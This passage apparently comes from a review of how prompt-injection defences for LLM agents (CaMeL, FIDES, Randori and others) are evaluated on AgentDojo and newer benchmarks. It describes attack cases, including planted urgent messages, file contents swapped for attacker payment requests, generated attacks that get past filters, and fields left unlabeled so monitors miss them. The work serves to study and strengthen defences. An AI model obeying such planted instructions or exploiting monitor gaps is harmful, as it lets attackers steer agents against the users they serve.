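The attack figures also combine the protection that labels provide with the protection an agent gets from planning before it reads. Garby and colleagues sorted the 144 banking pairs by whether a program written for the user's task could plausibly carry out the attack, and in 97 pairs it could not. For example, a program that only summarises recent transactions never calls the payment tool. An agent that plans first will resist such attacks without labels.

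Even the other 47 pairs, which are harder and should test the label checks better, left the checks very little to stop. With the checks off, CaMeL resisted all 141 runs of these pairs with GPT-5.2 and 138 of 141 with MiMo-v2.5.

Planning in advance failed in one task, where the user asks the agent to follow a file's instructions precisely. With checks off, CaMeL's planning model wrote a loop that could read instructions from the file and call whichever tool each one named. Although the program was fixed beforehand, the file's contents determined which actions it took. An attack succeeded this way once with each of the two models.

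Randori's two failures in 1,296 attacked runs came from the same combination of user task and attack. The user asked the agent to make a payment by following instructions in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents with their own payment request. The planning model had endorsed the file, and when Garby and colleagues disabled endorsement, the monitor blocked the attack. One of the two successful attacks in CaMeL's original evaluation also involved a payment directed by a document. In the other, the agent quoted hotel reviews word for word, and AgentDojo's scoring function counted the attack as successful because the quotation contained the attacker's phrase. The same kind of match caused the only recorded failure of TACIT, the Scala system, in 1,926 trials.

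### Newer models ignore the standard attack

AgentDojo's best-known attack presents the planted text as an important message that the agent must deal with before the user's task. *APPA* reports that GPT-4o followed such text in 31 per cent of attempts, whereas GPT-5.6 Luna never followed it in 160 office runs without a defence. GPT-5.6 Luna also followed no planted text in a further 60 runs with five families of attack. A defence tested with such a model will show zero successful attacks even if its monitor does nothing.

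*aiAuthZ* (2026) found the same with Fable 5 and Gemini 3 Flash on 20 banking pairs. No attack succeeded without a defence, so adding a strict list of permitted actions could not improve that result. The list cut task completion without attacks from 100 to 80 per cent because it blocked a legitimate first payment to a new payee. But it also blocked seven attacker-directed calls that the models made under attack, so the planted text had some effect on the models.

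Attack success rates don't measure whether an agent can still complete the user's tasks while under attack. In the undefended tests, Gemini 3 Flash completed 60 per cent of the user tasks under attack and Fable 5 completed none. An attacker who can't get the agent to make a payment may still be able to keep it from doing its job.

Resistance to a fixed attack text is also weak evidence of resistance to new ones. *AutoDojo* (2026) generates attacks instead of reusing the standard wording. On DeepSeek-v4-Pro, the standard attack succeeded less than 10 per cent of the time without a defence, and a filter called PIGuard reduced this to zero. But the generated attacks succeeded against the filtered agent in 8.2 per cent of all cases and 13.2 per cent of banking cases. The filter also cut the share of tasks the agent completed without attacks from 89.5 to 54.4 per cent.

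Attacks succeeded more often when the user's request was vague. On the banking tasks, generated attacks against an undefended Gemini 2.5 Flash succeeded 66.7 per cent of the time when the request left the choice of action most open, and 13.9 per cent when it was fully specified. A benchmark made up mostly of precise requests will therefore underestimate the risk to users who leave more decisions to the agent.

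A developer can also test the monitor without waiting for a model to be fooled. *Bounded Agents* (2026) inserts the attacker's tool call just after the agent's first legitimate call, similar to the simulated injections that Zhou and colleagues used to test ELBA. This method suits systems meant to be safe whatever the model does, because the result doesn't depend on how well the model resists the attack.

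*APPA* took a milder approach with 2026 models. In half of its runs, extra instructions encouraged the agent to take shortcuts and follow embedded directions. On AgentThreatBench, attacks then succeeded in 40 to 69 per cent of runs without effective checks and in none of the runs with *APPA*. They succeeded in 5 to 31 per cent of runs with the paper's own two configurations of FIDES. These configurations left some paths unchecked, so the result doesn't contradict FIDES's zero on AgentDojo.

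### Labels taken from the attacks

AgentDojo comes without labels, so anyone who tests information-flow control on it has to add them. Costa and colleagues labeled a field untrusted if any AgentDojo attack targets it. Because some attacks use the body of an email, they labeled every email body untrusted, including those from coworkers. They also labeled each email as readable by its sender and recipients.

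This choice makes the test easier for the monitor because the labels are guaranteed to cover every place where the benchmark plants an instruction. A company that deploys an agent has no list of such places. If someone moved an attack into a field labeled trusted, the integrity check would not respond to it. The test shows that the monitor stops attacks when the labels are right, but it doesn't measure how often developers would label fields correctly.

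The same choice can make the agent look less useful. A real mail system can often authenticate a sender, and a company might reasonably trust some of its own employees' messages. Costa and colleagues avoided such judgments to get a clear baseline. With finer labels, the agent might have completed more tasks, but more attacks might also have got through.

FIDES's developers also used the office tasks to adjust the instructions they gave GPT-4o, then reused those instructions everywhere else. The office scores may therefore overstate FIDES's performance a little.

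### Completed tasks that were guesses

The completion score is also flawed because it counts correct guesses as successes. Costa and colleagues tested a version of their agent with variables alone, which shouldn't be able to solve any travel task. With GPT-4o and no checks, it still scored 43 per cent on the travel tasks, partly because it sometimes guessed, such as when it picked the right hotel without seeing any ratings. In a banking task, it correctly identified a New Year's gift because the account had only one transaction on 1 January.

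With o1, the version that couldn't read the reviews scored 2 per cent on travel, probably because o1 obeyed the instruction to stop when it needed hidden information, while GPT-4o carried on. A benchmark that checks only the final answer gives the worse behaviour a higher score. With GPT-4o, that version scored 44 per cent under the same checks as FIDES, which casts doubt on FIDES's own 41 per cent.

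An agent can pass some tasks by doing nothing. In one, the user asks it to pay a bill like last month's, and the correct response is to stop because the details are missing. An agent that can't read the data passes this task without finding that the details are missing.

Attack scores can also make a defence look better than it is. *Bounded Agents* found that some attacks didn't count as successes even though the attacker's tool call had run. The scoring function checks the full state of the task, and in these runs the agent hadn't yet read the data that the attacker wanted.

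### What the tasks leave out

AgentDojo's standard attack targets the agent's model and isn't written for any of these defences. Better wording can't change a conservative label, so an attacker facing a monitor would look for wrong labels and for harmful actions that the policy permits, such as the earlier payment to a false account number. Wording does matter against RTBAS or FlowSeal, because a model estimates the labels or judges the output.

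AgentDojo also mostly tests instructions planted in outside data. Kim, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI*, list five other ways to attack an agent:

- supplying harmful data that contains no instructions, such as a malicious software package;
- altering a tool or its description;
- adding instructions to the user's own request;
- planting hidden behaviour in the model;
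- corrupting the agent's stored memory.

A score of zero on AgentDojo says nothing about these attacks, several of which fall outside the threat model of Costa and colleagues.

Some newer benchmarks are harder for systems that rely on labels. AgentDyn puts the information that the user needs and the planted instruction in the same document. *Environment Steering* (2026) points out that this leaves no trustworthy source, so its monitor has to examine the content. Across five models, its policies lowered attack success on AgentDyn by an average of 40.9 per cent. On AgentDojo, they stopped every attack against Kimi K2.5 but also blocked some safe actions by that model, which had been nearly perfect without them.

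Short tasks hide label creep, because a restricted context does little damage if no work remains. *APPA* leaves out AgentDojo partly for this reason, since that benchmark's tasks tend to end once the agent has read something and acted on it. *SPA* addresses this with a version of AgentDojo in which later requests depend on data that the agent stored earlier, and it measures whether the agent retrieves that data.

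Few tests measure how much an agent's choice of action reveals about confidential data. AgentDojo's functions check whether the attacker's goal was met, which usually means a particular payment, message or deletion. They would miss a leak such as a meeting-room booking that reveals a merger, so FIDES's AgentDojo results don't measure how much information leaks this way.

### What a better test would record

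To measure a leak through actions, a tester could run the agent many times with each of two secrets and keep everything else the same. Suppose it books a room in a share p of the runs with a merger memo and in a share q of the runs without one. An observer who sees only whether there was a booking, and who considers both memos equally likely, can guess correctly with probability at most

½ + ½|p − q|.

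If the agent books a room in 90 of 100 runs with the merger and 20 of 100 without it, the observer is right 85 per cent of the time. If the two rates are equal, the observer can only guess. When many different actions are visible, the tester replaces |p − q| with half the sum of the absolute differences between each action's probability with the merger and without it. The tester would need many runs, because a model's random choices also produce differences in small samples.

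For attacks, a test should record what reached a recipient or changed in a file, as Singh and Srinivasa's work on permission guards does. It should also score the user's task and the attack together. In *APPA*'s results across three models, one FIDES configuration completed all 150 runs of the memory tasks under ordinary instructions, while *APPA* completed only 71. But that configuration didn't check what passed from memory to the user, and 103 of 150 memory attacks succeeded when the instructions encouraged risky behaviour. Counting only tasks completed without a successful attack would have exposed the unchecked path.

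Tests should also report why runs fail. A run may fail because the monitor refused a necessary action, the model used a variable wrongly, or the planner never produced a usable plan. *SPA* records whether each run reached execution or stopped earlier. *Data Leakage Prevention in Agentic Applications via Preemptive Hardening* (2026) argues for also recording whether a defence makes the agent invent unsupported answers or fall back on unsafe behaviour. Tests should count requests for human approval separately, as Kolluri and colleagues do.

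Whoever writes the labels and policies should do so before seeing the attacks, and testers should publish them with the scores. Testers should test each defence against the standard attacks, attacks designed to get around its specific rules, and forced tool calls that simulate a model under the attacker's control. They should also run the same agent with its checks on and off to show what the checks contributed.

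Finally, a system that resists every attack in a test may still have a true resistance rate below 100 per cent. Randori with Qwen3.7-plus resisted the harder banking attacks in all 141 runs, but these were 47 pairs, each run three times. Garby and colleagues calculate that this result is compatible with a true resistance rate as low as 92.4 per cent, even for attacks of the same kind.
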